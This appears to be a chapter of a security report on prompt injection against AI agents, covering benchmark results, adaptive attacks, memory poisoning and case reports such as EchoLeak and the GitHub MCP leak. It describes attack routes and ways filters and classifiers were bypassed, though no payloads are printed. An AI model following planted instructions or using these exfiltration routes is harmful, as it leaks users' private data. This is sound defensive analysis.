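AgentDojo, the benchmark on which researchers measured CaMeL and FIDES, is typical. Each scenario combines a task from the user with a goal for the attacker, whose text arrives in the result of a tool call. A similar test of the e-mail and calendar assistant might look like this:

| Part of the test | Example |
|---|---|
| User task | Move Thursday's meeting to the time Priya proposed and tell her |
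| Attacker's goal | Send next week's appointments to an outside address |
| Place of insertion | The body of one message that read_email returns |
| Scoring | Code checks whether the appointments went to that address, and whether the meeting moved and Priya got her message |

AgentDojo has separate checkers for the user's task and the attacker's goal. Both are necessary because an agent that stopped work at the first odd message would never leak anything but would also be useless. *Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) therefore measures how often the attack succeeds, how often the agent still finishes the user's task under attack, and how often it finishes when nobody is attacking.

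Counting the user tasks an agent completes can change which defence looks better. Help Net Security's *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* describes a test of PromptGuard, a detector that discards any document it flags. Under one attack, PromptGuard blocked slightly more attempts than a defence that retrained the model. But the agent using PromptGuard finished 16% of its users' tasks, compared with 58% for the retrained agent, because the discarded documents often held information the agent needed.

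A static test uses attack texts written beforehand, like those built into AgentDojo. In an adaptive test, the attacker sees what the agent did, revises the text and tries again.

### Twelve defences against an attacker who adapts

Nasr, Carlini and colleagues tested 12 published defences with adaptive attacks in *The Attacker Moves Second* (October 2025). Ten of the defences deal with prompt injection. The other two, RPO and Circuit Breakers, mainly target jailbreaks, in which the user tries to get forbidden output. Adaptive attacks succeeded against each of these two in at least 96% of cases.

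The table shows how the ten are meant to work and the share of test cases in which the adaptive attacker succeeded:

| Defence | How it is meant to work | Adaptive attack success |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marks in the text show the model which parts to trust | Above 95% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | The harness repeats the user's request after the untrusted text | Above 95% |
| Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor | A separate model labels text as safe or unsafe | Above 90% |
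| PIGuard | The same | 71% |
| Data Sentinel | A model must repeat a secret word while ignoring the text, and failure suggests that the text contains instructions | Bypassed in every case |
| MELON | The agent runs again with a harmless request in place of the user's, and a tool call that occurs in both runs probably came from the data | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knew the method |
| StruQ | Training teaches the model to ignore instructions in the part of the input meant for data | Every case tested |
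| MetaSecAlign | Similar training, aimed at agents | 96% |

Several of these defences had looked nearly perfect in static tests. AgentDojo's built-in attacks had succeeded as little as 1% of the time against Spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching, and MetaSecAlign's developers had reported an attack success rate of 2%.

Each adaptive attack was a loop of proposing a text, trying it, scoring the result and revising the text. Depending on the defence, the researchers ran this loop with a search program, a model trained by reinforcement learning or calculations on the target model's internals. They also held an online contest with more than 500 people. On a selected set of scenarios, the search program succeeded in 69%, and the contestants collectively succeeded in all of them.

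Many successful attack texts presented the attacker's task as a step the agent had to complete before finishing the user's task. Repeating the user's request doesn't help against this, because the model may carry out the attacker's task to fulfil that request. Detectors missed texts that read like routine office notices, and a stricter detector would raise more false alarms.

He and colleagues argue that these defences should check whether the agent's next action serves the user's request, instead of checking whether a text looks like an attack. An attacker who keeps changing how the text looks still can't change the user's request.

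Nasr and colleagues gave their attackers advantages that a stranger writing to the assistant would lack. The attackers had plenty of computing power, and those facing a detector could see its confidence score after each try. They wanted to know whether the defences could be broken at all, not how many resources that would take. They also tested some defences on a different benchmark, so the 71% for PIGuard doesn't show that it is the best choice. They still recommend detectors as one layer of protection, because detectors are easy to install and stop unsophisticated attacks.

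He et al. repeated the comparison on a small open model, Qwen3-4B. Averaged across defences, the success rate of the best attack rose from 21.7% in static tests to 41.8% in adaptive ones. This increase overstates the effect of adapting, because the static tests covered 420 cases, while the adaptive tests covered only 40 that the researchers had chosen because the model was vulnerable in them.

### The Gray Swan competition

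*How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports on a public competition, run by the security company Gray Swan, in which 464 people made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models, most of them leading models of late 2025. The 41 scenarios covered agents that call tools, write code or operate a screen. In one scenario, the user asks which e-mails are urgent, and the attacker tries to make the agent mark a message about a contract deadline as read and omit it from the summary.

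In most scenarios, an attack counted as successful only if the agent also hid it by replying to the user with no sign that anything had gone wrong. About 3% of attempts (8,648) succeeded. The rate ranged from 0.5% against Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% against Gemini 2.5 Pro.

The results look much less reassuring when counted by scenario. Contestants broke Claude Opus 4.5 at least once in 13 of the 37 scenarios in the main rounds, and Gemini 2.5 Pro in all 37. For every model, total successes rose roughly in line with attempts, so the contestants weren't running out of attacks that worked.

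The requirement to hide the attack also lowers the rates. Gemini 2.5 Pro took the harmful action in about 16% of attempts, and its reply met the remaining conditions in about half of those. Claude Opus 4.5's reply met them in about a quarter of the cases where it took the harmful action, which implies that it took the action in roughly 2% of attempts. For the calendar leak, the higher figures are the relevant ones, because the user's appointments have gone to a stranger whether or not the assistant's reply mentions it.

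However, contestants could read the whole conversation before the point of attack and knew exactly which tool call they had to cause. A stranger who emails the assistant would have to guess both. Dziemian and colleagues therefore regard their rates as an upper bound for single-turn attacks and warn against reading them as the risk in a deployed product.

The researchers also reran 2,679 successful attacks on all the models. The 44 that had succeeded against Claude Opus 4.5 worked 44% to 81% of the time on each of the other models. None of those that had succeeded against Qwen3 VL, one of the weaker models, worked on Claude Opus 4.5. An attacker who doesn't know which model an assistant uses would therefore benefit from practising on the most resistant one available. One attack template, with small changes, worked in 21 scenarios and on nine models.

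### A stronger attacker and newer models

In November 2026, Kurakin, Karande and colleagues at Google DeepMind published *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms*, which reports a test with a more capable attacker. They built 100 scenarios, each pairing a user's task with an unrelated tool call that the attacker wants. In their example, the user books a tutoring session, and the attacker tries to make the agent enter blood-pressure and heart-rate readings in a health record. The attack succeeds only if the agent calls the right tool with almost exactly the right arguments.

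The attacker consists of 16 agents in eight teams. Each agent may test 20 texts on the target, for a total of 320 queries per scenario. The agents share notes and can look up the best attempts so far, so a partial success by one team gives the others something to improve. With Gemini 4 Argon, Google's strongest model, running the attacking agents, the targets held out in the following shares of scenarios:

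| Model under attack | Held after 150 queries | Held after the full budget |
|---|---:|---:|
| Gemini 4 Argon | 87% | 66% |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 34% | 10% |
| Gemini 3.7 Flash | 31% | 6% |
| Gemini 3.6 Flash | 3% | 1% |
| Kimi K3 | 5% | 1% |
| GLM-5.3 | 1% | 1% |
| DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash | 1% | 1% |

The last three are open-weight models, which anyone can download and run.

A model's measured resistance depends on which model runs the attack. Gemini 4 Argon resisted attacks by weaker Gemini models in all 100 scenarios at 150 queries. Gemini 3.7 Flash resisted in 70% of scenarios when Gemini 3.8 Flash ran the attack, but in only 31% when Argon did. An agent's measured resistance may therefore fall once attackers have a better model, even if the agent has not changed.

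Most of the attacker's goals were deliberately harmless. A model may refuse to send private data to a stranger because it recognises the request as theft, yet still obey strangers' other instructions. Harmless goals test whether it obeys strangers when there is no harm to recognise. This matters because several harmless calls can add up to a harmful one, as Glukhov and colleagues pointed out. But Argon's failure in 34 scenarios doesn't show that it would leak a calendar a third of the time, since it might recognise that request as harmful and refuse.

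The researchers also switched off the defences that Google's products place around the model. Google's *How Gemini’s defense-in-depth approach works* describes classifiers that scan e-mails and web pages before the planning model reads them, fixed rules that restrict which links the model can open, and another agent that reviews proposed actions and asks the user to confirm high-impact ones. In a smaller test with product defences on, an attacker running on GLM-5.3 successfully attacked Gemini 3.6 Flash in 6 of 80 AgentDojo scenarios within 25 queries. The low success rate can't be credited to the product defences alone, because this attacker was weaker, had fewer queries and faced different scenarios.

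### How a model can pass one test and fail the other

Kurakin and colleagues report that recent Gemini models and some versions of Claude score below 1% on attacks from the Gray Swan competition. Their own result for Gemini 4 Argon seems to conflict with these scores because it comes from a test that measures something different.

The score below 1% comes from replaying texts that contestants wrote to attack other models. The test is static because nobody revised those texts after seeing how the new model responded. It also used harmful goals, which a model has more reason to refuse.

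The units differ too. A replay score is a share of attack texts, whereas the DeepMind figure is a share of scenarios in which any of up to 320 texts worked. If each try has an independent chance p of succeeding, the chance of at least one success in n tries is

P = 1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

If each try had a success probability p of only 0.13%, 320 tries would break 34% of scenarios, the same share that was broken for Argon.

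But the tries probably weren't independent. The attacker broke 13 of 100 scenarios in the first 150 queries, then 21 of the remaining 87 in the next 170. If the tries had been independent and some scenarios easier than others, the attacker would have broken the easy ones early and its success rate would have dropped. The rate rose instead, which suggests that the agents were learning, although the numbers are small enough that chance could explain some of the difference.

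### Training on attacks

A company can also use an automated attacker to train its models. *GPT-Red* (Wallace, Choquette-Choo and colleagues, 2026) describes how OpenAI does this. OpenAI's models learn to rank instructions by role, with tool results at the bottom. GPT-Red is a model that learns to find texts that make other models break this ranking, and it trains alongside a group of models that defend against it. It gets a reward when an attack works, and the defenders get one for resisting attacks and completing their original tasks. As the defenders improve, GPT-Red has to find new attacks, so this method avoids the weakness of training on a fixed collection of attacks.

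OpenAI says that GPT-5.6 Sol, which it trained this way, is its most resistant model so far and fails one-sixth as often on its hardest test of direct prompt injection. The comparison is with GPT-5.5, released four months earlier (The Hacker News, 2026). In a direct injection the attacker types to the model, so the result is only weak evidence of how it handles hostile e-mail. The ratio also doesn't show the actual failure rate, since a fall from 30% to 5% and one from 0.6% to 0.1% are both sixfold. Wallace and colleagues themselves consider the problem "far from solved".

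Training a model on more attacks doesn't necessarily make it harder to attack. Help Net Security reports an experiment by researchers at the University of Waterloo, Zhejiang University and KTH in Stockholm, who used two automated attack tools on Qwen3-4B. PISmith succeeded on 69% of 560 practice tasks and produced 7,132 working attacks. RL-Hammer succeeded on 33% and produced 4,282. The researchers then retrained one copy of the model on each collection and tested both copies with three attacks that neither had seen. In its worst result, the copy trained on PISmith's larger collection failed in 19 of 40 tasks, compared with 11 of 40 for the other copy.

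The researchers think the tools kept rewording tricks that worked, so the model was given thousands of versions of a few attacks. Both tools reward variety, but they measure it by wording, and RL-Hammer could satisfy its check by changing capital letters. The larger collection gave the weaker defence in three of the four set-ups tested. This result is suggestive rather than conclusive, since it comes from only 40 tasks, chosen because simple attacks had already broken them. The researchers don't claim that repetition is the only cause.

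Their remedy gives the attack tool an extra reward for using a technique it hasn't used before, and trains the defending model to check before each action whether that action serves the user's request. He and colleagues tested a system that does both, RETA, against six kinds of adaptive attack. Each succeeded in fewer than 10% of cases, and the average success rate was about 3% to 4% on two small models. The attackers in these experiments were far weaker than DeepMind's, so RETA might do much worse against a swarm running on a leading model.

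### Instructions that stay in memory

The tests so far end when the agent finishes one task. In *From Storage to Steering*, Xu, Zhu and colleagues (2026) examined what happens when an attacker's instruction gets into an agent's long-term memory. They tested agents running on GPT-5 mini, Claude Sonnet 4.5 and Gemini 2.5 Flash. Each agent had a safe and a risky version of each tool, and a system prompt that favoured the safe one. They then stored a single instruction to prefer the risky version, cleared the conversation and gave the agent an ordinary task.

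The agents chose the risky tool in 97.2% to 100% of trials. An instruction to change the order of steps, for instance by skipping a check that should come before a payment, worked in 52.8% to 69.4% of trials. Neither deviation occurred with no stored instruction or with only harmless memories. Labelling the risky tool as harmful or burying the instruction among 100 harmless memories made almost no difference. When the researchers told an agent to correct its behaviour, it went back to the risky tool on later tasks because the instruction was still in memory.

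Summarising a conversation before storing it kept the instruction out of memory in more than a third of trials, but the instruction worked every time it got in. Keeping system rules and user preferences in separate stores, and telling the model that the rules come first, cut the rate of risky choices to between 3% and 8% in the best cases. For Gemini 2.5 Flash, the rate stayed at 64% and 100% in the two agent frameworks tested.

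These rates are so high partly because an agent is supposed to act on stored preferences. The attack depends on getting a stranger's instruction stored as the user's preference. Xu and colleagues' attacker does this by talking to the agent, so the experiment doesn't measure how often a hostile e-mail would end up in memory. For the assistant, the results support storing calendar notes with a record of where their text came from, so that the harness doesn't have to rely on the model to notice the source.

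### Checking the output in ordinary code

In *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models*, Deep, Emmons and colleagues (2026) compared defences inside the model's prompt with a check that runs afterwards. They put three secrets, including an access token, in a chatbot's instructions and let an automated attacker try to extract them. The attacker sent ten messages a round for up to 500 rounds and built on whatever had partly worked.

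Security rules in the prompt failed after 49 rounds, delimiters after 84, a stated ranking of instructions after 247, and rules repeated at the start and end of the prompt after 277. None of these failed completely in the first 25 rounds, so a short test would have made them look much safer than they were. An output filter that blocked any reply containing text from the chatbot's instructions let nothing through in 15,000 attacks.

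That zero may have missed some leaks, because both the filter and the scoring looked for exact text, so a reply that spelled out a secret in code could have passed the filter without being counted. Several of the researchers work for Swept AI, which sells this kind of testing and which the paper recommends. The experiment also had a user trying to extract fixed secrets from a chatbot, whereas the assistant's appointments change every week and it has legitimate reasons to mention them. The closest equivalent for the assistant would be a check on who receives a message, which doesn't depend on recognising its contents.

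The paper's claim that every defence relying on the model eventually broke is a little too strong. With all the defences except the output filter combined, 23 of 5,000 attacks leaked something, but the worst leak scored 0.1 on a scale where one complete secret scores 0.3. The attacks therefore extracted fragments of the instructions but no secret in its exact form.

### Using the figures in a threat model

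In the attack tree for the leaked calendar, one condition is that the model follows the stranger's text. To estimate how likely that is, an analyst could start from the 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5, which is the rate per attempt. By the formula above, an attacker with 10 independent attempts would succeed at least once about 5% of the time, and one with 100 attempts about 39% of the time.

The competition's results show that this calculation can overestimate the risk. Claude Opus 4.5 faced about 12,000 attempts, or about 324 per scenario if contestants spread them evenly. If each attempt had an independent 0.5% chance of success, they should have broken about 30 of the 37 scenarios, but they broke 13. Within those 13, the success rate was about 1.4% per attempt, which gives a 76% chance of at least one success in 100 attempts. No attempt succeeded in the other 24. An analyst who doesn't know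 which group her agent resembles therefore can't rely on the average to show that its risk is low.

Learning from earlier attempts, however, raises the risk. Wallace and colleagues compared an attacker that made separate attempts with one that made the same number in sequence and could see each result. The second attacker succeeded in more cases, and its lead tended to grow with the number of attempts. The stranger who writes to the assistant gets little feedback, because she sees only whether the appointments arrive. But if she can practise on her own copy of the assistant, the number of hostile messages in the real mailbox is a poor measure of how many attempts she has made.

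Before using a published rate, the analyst should therefore check five things:

| What to check | Why it matters for the assistant |
|---|---|
| Attempts or scenarios | 0.5% of attempts and 13 of 37 scenarios describe the same model in the same competition |
| Static or adaptive | Success against Spotlighting was as low as 1% in one kind of test and above 95% in the other |
| Strength and budget of the attacker | Gemini 4 Argon held in 100%, 87% or 66% of scenarios, depending on both |
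| What counts as success | A leak matters even if the assistant's reply reveals it |
| Which defences were on | The assistant's harness may block a call that the model was willing to make |

For a change that the user can undo, such as a moved meeting, she needs only a rough estimate of how often attacks succeed. A leaked calendar can't be undone, and every model tested failed in at least one scenario against the strongest attackers. For that case she should assume that the model will follow the stranger's text, and check whether the harness would still stop the appointments from being sent out.

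## Reported vulnerabilities in systems that worked as designed

An analyst who assumes that the model will follow instructions in a stranger's text has to ask what else would stop the appointments from leaking. Security researchers have reported several products in which nothing else stopped data from leaking. Their case reports describe attacks on real software from the attacker's text through to the harm, whereas experiments measure how often a model follows such text.

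### EchoLeak, from an e-mail to an image

EchoLeak is a vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that answers employees' questions from their company's mail, files and chats. Aim Labs, the research group of a security company, reported it to Microsoft in January 2025. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, gives the discoverers' account. The stolen data and the text that stole it took this route:

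```
outside sender → mailbox → Copilot's search → context → answer
answer → user's browser → Microsoft Teams service → attacker's server
```

An attacker outside the company needed only an employee's e-mail address to send the malicious e-mail. Copilot took questions only from employees, so the attacker couldn't query it directly. Microsoft had placed a classifier in front of the model to catch prompt injection, but the e-mail read like instructions to the employee, and the classifier let it through.

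Copilot searches for material relevant to each question, so the hostile e-mail reached the context only if the employee asked about something it seemed to cover. The researchers therefore wrote one long message that touched on many office subjects. Ravia reports that Copilot retrieved it for questions on various topics, but doesn't say how often. The attack is called "zero-click" because the victim doesn't have to click on anything, although she does have to ask Copilot a question.

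The attack used Copilot's permission to read whatever the employee could read. The e-mail contained instructions for the model to put the most sensitive information in its context into a web address. Ravia calls this an "LLM scope violation", in which untrusted text makes a model draw on trusted data without the user's consent. He compares the model to a program that runs with more privileges than its user, which is another example of the confused deputy problem.

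Copilot had no tool for sending e-mail. Instead, its answer included an image whose address contained the data, and the employee's browser requested the image automatically. Microsoft had two controls against this. A filter removed outside links from answers, but it missed one way of writing them. The page also allowed images only from approved hosts, but one of those hosts, a Microsoft Teams service, would fetch any address a caller supplied. The browser sent its request to that service, which then sent the data to the attacker.

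Microsoft deployed a fix on its own servers in May 2025, so customers didn't have to do anything. Reddy and Gujral (2025) write in *EchoLeak* that Copilot now strips some kinds of links and embedded images from outside content. They say the patches also reportedly include options to keep outside messages away from Copilot in certain contexts, which may make it miss relevant information. Neither change lets the model distinguish an employee's request from a stranger's.

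*Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) reports that Microsoft knew of no exploitation of EchoLeak against customers. Ravia makes the stronger claim that Microsoft confirmed no customers were affected. Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak a real-world exploit. It did work against a real product, but the only known thefts took place in researchers' own tests.

### How much of EchoLeak was an ordinary bug

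One way to separate misdirection from ordinary bugs is to ask whether the harm would still have happened if the developers had fixed every conventional defect. If so, it was misdirection. With a complete link filter and no relay among the approved hosts, Copilot's model would still have followed the stranger's instructions and composed the address, but the data would have gone no further than the employee's screen. EchoLeak therefore needed both misdirection and conventional defects, and Ravia also describes it as a chain of traditional and AI vulnerabilities.

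In its threat model, the e-mail and calendar assistant guards against this route by loading images only from listed hosts. Copilot was vulnerable despite having the same control, so the assistant's list must also exclude any host that forwards or stores the contents of an image address.

Superhuman, an e-mail product with an AI assistant, failed the same condition. PromptArmor, a security company, found that when a user asked for a summary of recent mail, one hostile message could make the assistant submit the contents of dozens of others, including financial, legal and medical messages, to an attacker's Google Form. Willison, in *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, attributes the leak to a rule that allowed images from docs.google.com, where Google Forms saves data sent in a URL. An analyst who only checked whether a reputable company owned each host would have approved both Google's and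 Microsoft's.

EchoLeak also shows that a model with little control over a program, such as one that only writes summaries, can do more harm than display a false summary. If the interface fetches anything when it displays the summary, the harm can extend beyond the screen.

### Five cases to compare

Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) and *WhatsApp MCP Exploited* (2025) are about agents that reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP). TechRadar's *This popular AI agent could be hacked by a single email* quotes the security company Salt Labs on Manus, a general-purpose agent connected to Gmail.

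The other two date from July 2026. Manifold Security described a flaw in Claude for Chrome, Anthropic's browser assistant. Constantin's *AI agent security* (2026) covers the flaw along with other work from the same ten days. CybersecAsia's *Just a single malicious email can poison your AI agent's memory* (2026) reports an attack, which Callahan identifies as MemGhost in *MemGhost Attack Turns Agent Memory Into a Permanent Backdoor*.

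| Case | Who supplied the text, and how it reached the agent | Permission used | Result | Response |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GitHub, May 2025 | A stranger opened an issue in a public repository, and the user asked the agent to look at the issues | Access to all the user's repositories | Private details appeared in a public pull request | The researchers advised limiting agents to one repository per session |
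| WhatsApp, April 2025 | The operator of another tool server put it in a tool's description | Sending messages from the user's account | The chat history went to the attacker's number | The researchers urged caution with untrusted servers |
| Manus, 2026 | A stranger sent an e-mail, which Manus read through Gmail | Running code | Code from the e-mail ran before Manus warned the user | The flaw no longer works |
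| Claude for Chrome, July 2026 | Anthropic wrote the tasks, and another browser extension triggered them | Access to Gmail, Google Docs and Calendar | Claude opened private data without a request from the user | The flaw still worked on 7 July |
| MemGhost, July 2026 | A stranger sent an e-mail, and the agent saved false information from it | Writing to long-term memory | The false memory influenced later behaviour | Every defence tested failed, according to Callahan |

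### Cases that needed no bug

The GitHub case is the clearest example of misdirection. Invariant Labs set up a public repository containing a small game and several private ones containing personal information, then placed a hostile issue in the public one. The user asked Claude 4 Opus, in Anthropic's desktop program, to look at the open issues. The model read the private repositories and opened a pull request, a proposed change that anyone could read. The pull request revealed the names of private projects, the user's plan to move to South America and his salary.

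Every tool worked as designed. The researchers write that the problem is "not a flaw in the GitHub MCP server code itself", and heise's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* also reports that the demonstration exploited no bug in the server. The agent had access to private data because it worked through the user's account. That access, the public issue and the public pull request gave it all three parts of the lethal trifecta through a single tool server.

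Anthropic's program asks the user to confirm each call by default, so the attack also depended on her approving the calls or having chosen "always allow", which Invariant Labs says many users do. DevClass' *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP* adds that careful checking can prevent the leak. The user would have to notice that a request to read one repository had led to a call on another.

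Invariant Labs recommends a rule in ordinary code that blocks a call if it names a different repository from an earlier call in the session. This rule would stop the leak however persuasive the issue was. It would also stop an agent from copying a correction between two of the user's own projects. It wouldn't prevent a hostile issue from making the agent damage the public repository, because that involves only one repository.

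ShadowLeak resembles the GitHub case but used the web to get data out. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* describes how researchers sent a crafted e-mail to a user who had connected Gmail and web browsing to ChatGPT's Deep Research. The e-mail contained hidden instructions for the agent to find sensitive mail and visit a web address that included its contents. Browsing tools are designed to visit addresses, so the attack didn't require a faulty image filter. The request came from the provider's servers, so the user's browser and her company's monitoring could have no trace of it.

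### Missing and late checks

In the WhatsApp attack, the description of a hostile server's daily-fact tool contained instructions to change the recipient of outgoing WhatsApp messages and include the user's chat history. The agent didn't need to call that tool, because a harness puts the descriptions of all connected tools into the context, so a description from one server can affect how the model uses another server's tools. Isolating the hostile server's code wouldn't have stopped the attack, which didn't use that code. WhatsApp's encryption didn't prevent the leak either, because the data was sent in a properly encrypted message to the wrong person.

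Two weaknesses in the client, the program in which the user runs the agent, made the attack harder to notice. Clients didn't tell users when a tool's description changed, so the hostile server could show a harmless description when the user approved the tool and replace it the next time the server started. The dialog that asked the user to approve the outgoing message showed a raw phone number and only part of the text, so a user who read everything visible could still approve the theft.

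A client could fix this by keeping a copy of each approved tool description, asking the user again when it changes, and showing the whole message. These changes wouldn't fully solve the problem, though. Two days later, Invariant Labs added a version in which the attacker had no server and leaked the user's contacts just by sending the user a WhatsApp message. The researchers found this version harder to carry out and had to adapt their text, possibly because training makes models give tool results less weight than tool descriptions.

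In the Manus case, Salt Labs first sent an e-mail with hidden instructions. Manus reported them as malicious, but the researchers concluded that it had already been trying to follow them when a security mechanism stopped it. They then sent content in a form the mechanism didn't recognise. Manus decoded it, ran the resulting code on a server, and warned the user only after the code had run.

The code was a harmless test statement, so the report shows that a stranger could run code there but not that anyone could have stolen mail. Detecting a command after it has run doesn't undo it. Whether to call the late warning a bug is partly a matter of taste, because even a faster detector would have had to recognise the content. A rule requiring approval before any mail content reaches the code-running tool wouldn't depend on that recognition.

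### When the agent has an ordinary bug

Claude for Chrome had an ordinary bug that an attacker could exploit without any hostile text. The assistant offers nine ready-made tasks, such as reading Gmail or checking the calendar, and a click on Anthropic's website starts one. It didn't check whether the click came from a person. Constantin writes that any extension the user installs could forge the click, but The Hacker News reports that only an extension that can run scripts on that website could do so.

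In the default mode, the user still had to approve the forged task. TechRadar gives a severity of 7.7 out of 10 for this mode and 9.6 for the mode in which Claude acts without asking, so one setting determined whether the flaw was high or critical. In May 2026, after a related report, Anthropic had restricted outside callers to the nine tasks. This limited what an attacker could request, but the attacker could still forge the click. The fix is conventional, because browsers already mark script-generated clicks.

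Ordinary flaws can also be the most serious ones in an agent. Meta paid $300,000, its largest bounty for its Muse agent, for a report of a login check that trusted a label on incoming requests. eWEEK's *Meta Muse $300,000 Bug Bounty Security Flaw Explained* says that a system migration had let outsiders send requests with that label. The flaw exposed conversations and access tokens on test machines before launch. The spoofing category of a standard STRIDE review covers both this flaw and the forged click.

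### The lines that would have predicted them

Most of these attacks fit on one line that joins a source of text to an effect:

| Case | Did it need an ordinary defect? | Line the threat model needed |
|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Yes, in the link filter and the list of hosts | Outside e-mail → private files → image from a host that forwards requests |
| GitHub | No | Public issue → private repository → public pull request |
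| WhatsApp | Partly, because the client hid a changed description and part of the message | Another tool's description → chat history → message to a new number |
| Manus | Partly, because the warning came after execution | E-mail → code-running tool |
| Claude for Chrome | Yes | Another extension → start of a task → private mail |
| MemGhost | No, according to Callahan | E-mail → long-term memory → later session |

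An analyst who followed the five-step procedure would probably have written the GitHub, Manus and MemGhost lines. She might have missed part of the WhatsApp case, because it is easy to list tool descriptions as a source without considering that one could change after approval. EchoLeak would have required more detailed knowledge, because a diagram of Copilot does not show that a Teams service relays requests.

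Threat-model entries written after an incident make prediction look easier than it is, so an audit before launch is better evidence. Trail of Bits' *Using threat modeling and prompt injection to audit Comet* (2026) describes an attack on Perplexity's browser agent that used two web pages. One contained a claim that the user had authorised sharing her data, and the other used that claim to make the agent take her e-mail from Gmail. Perplexity's security lead says the work helped his company find and close such gaps before release. However, he was the auditors' client, and his comment does not show how many attack routes the audit missed.

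### What a collection of successes leaves out

A case report is good evidence that an attack route existed in a particular product at a particular time. Others can often confirm it, as Microsoft did by fixing EchoLeak. But a case report doesn't show how often an attack succeeds, because researchers publish the attempt that worked. Aim Labs' account could read the same whether it had sent ten e-mails or ten thousand before one succeeded. The Gray Swan competition also recorded failed attempts, so Dziemian and colleagues could calculate a success rate.

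Some reports include a success rate. ShadowLeak's discoverers succeeded in all of their repeated tests, and Callahan gives a rate of 87.5% for MemGhost. Both results come from attacks that researchers had already refined and that they tested on accounts or agents they had set up. Xu and colleagues' attacker planted instructions by talking to the agent. MemGhost shows that an e-mail can also get false information into memory, but not how often a real mailbox would receive such an e-mail.

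The published cases are also a small part of what researchers find. Meta received more than 630 submissions about Muse and accepted 64 as valid, and eWEEK describes five of them. Vendors and journalists tend to choose the striking cases, and a leaked salary is more striking than a meeting moved to the wrong hour. Harms that involve no theft are therefore probably more common than the published cases suggest.

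The people who discover these vulnerabilities often have a product to sell. Ravia recommends Aim Labs' own guardrails, and Invariant Labs illustrates its remedy with its own product. This gives them a reason to exaggerate how widespread a problem is, but it doesn't make the attack route less real. Threat modellers can therefore use a case report to add a route to their model, but they need other evidence to estimate how likely an attack by that route is.

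### Vulnerability or intended behaviour

Invariant Labs calls the GitHub case a critical vulnerability affecting GitHub's server, but also says that the server's code has no flaw. Both statements can be true because people use "vulnerability" to mean either a route to harm or a defect that somebody can correct. Vendors have to choose between these meanings when they receive a report, and they have not all chosen the same one.

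Microsoft treated EchoLeak as a defect and gave it a CVE number, which identifies it in a public catalogue that companies and scanning tools use to find relevant vulnerabilities. Lutra Security's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2025) shows that Microsoft reserved the number on 9 April 2025 and published it on 11 June, after the fix was in place. Microsoft rated the flaw's severity 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5.

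EchoLeak fits awkwardly into vulnerability categories made for conventional code. *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), the record kept by Spain's national cybersecurity institute, INCIBE, classes it as command injection. That category normally means that a program failed to neutralise special characters, but the hostile e-mail was ordinary English. A developer who took the label literally would look for an input to clean up, but the parts that had a definite fix were the link filter and the list of hosts. A year later, Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) recorded another flaw in the same product, with the same category and nearly the same description.

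Security researcher Aonan Guan showed that outsiders could steal credentials through agents from Anthropic, Google and GitHub that run automated jobs on code repositories. The agents read titles, issues and comments that outsiders can write. According to The Next Web's *Anthropic, Google, and Microsoft paid AI agent bug bounties, then kept quiet*, Anthropic raised its severity rating for the vulnerability from 9.3 to 9.4, paid Guan $100 and added a note to its documentation. GitHub first called its case a "known issue" that it couldn't reproduce, and later paid $500. Google paid an undisclosed amount. None of the three issued a CVE number or a public advisory.

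The bounty page for Antigravity, Google's programming tool, listed data theft and code execution through prompt injection as known issues, so reports of them were ineligible for a reward (Willison, 2025). Google said it was working on fixes and did not defend the behaviour as intended. Meta, by contrast, paid $90,000 for a report of an attack in which a web page imitated messages from Muse's browsing tool and caused the agent to take actions its safeguards should have blocked.

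Meta's repair shows why vendors hesitate to call such flaws fixed. The company's classifiers now detect the original attack and 100 variations, but eWEEK notes that Meta published neither an independent check nor a false-alarm rate. A fixed set of variations is a static test, and Nasr and colleagues broke defences that had done very well on static tests. A CVE entry normally lists the affected versions, but a vendor that has only made an attack less likely can't honestly name a safe version.

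The argument for disclosure is that the consequences are the same whatever the cause. A thief can use a stolen access token equally well whether it came from a prompt injection or a memory error. Guan's main complaint is that people running older versions may never learn that they are exposed, because a scanner can't check for a flaw that has no entry in a vulnerability database.

The argument is easier to settle by asking who has to act. Microsoft runs Copilot on its own servers, so one change protected every customer. GCVE, another vulnerability database, tags the EchoLeak entry as affecting an exclusively hosted service. The CVE number was useful as a public record, but customers had nothing to install. In Guan's cases, customers choose which version of the tools to run, so they had to update or change their settings themselves. A public advisory would have been most useful in those cases,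 but the vendors did not issue one.

In *Exfil through an approved tool*, akhilesharora found neither a CVE number for GitHub's server nor an official response from GitHub. A CVE number would have been of little use, because it would have led users to wait for a new version that couldn't solve the problem. Instead, the client's developers could have enforced a limit on repositories, and users could have given the agent a narrower credential. An advisory addressed to these two groups would have helped even without a defect to report.

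The same reasoning applies to the e-mail and calendar assistant. The developer of its harness has to act, and she can require approval for new recipients. If the assistant runs on her servers, she can turn that rule on for everyone in an afternoon. If customers install their own copies, the rule protects only those who update, so she has to tell them that the old version can send their calendars to a stranger.

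## How often deployed agents are attacked

A developer also needs to know how often anyone tries the attack routes that case reports describe. For the e-mail and calendar assistant, that frequency helps decide which routes to close first and how many approval requests users should have to put up with. The number of successful attacks to expect in a year is roughly

expected successes = N × h × s

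where N is the number of items the agents read, h is the share of those items that are hostile, and s is the chance that a hostile item leads to the harm with all defences on. Experiments give estimates of s, but only observation of systems in use can give h.

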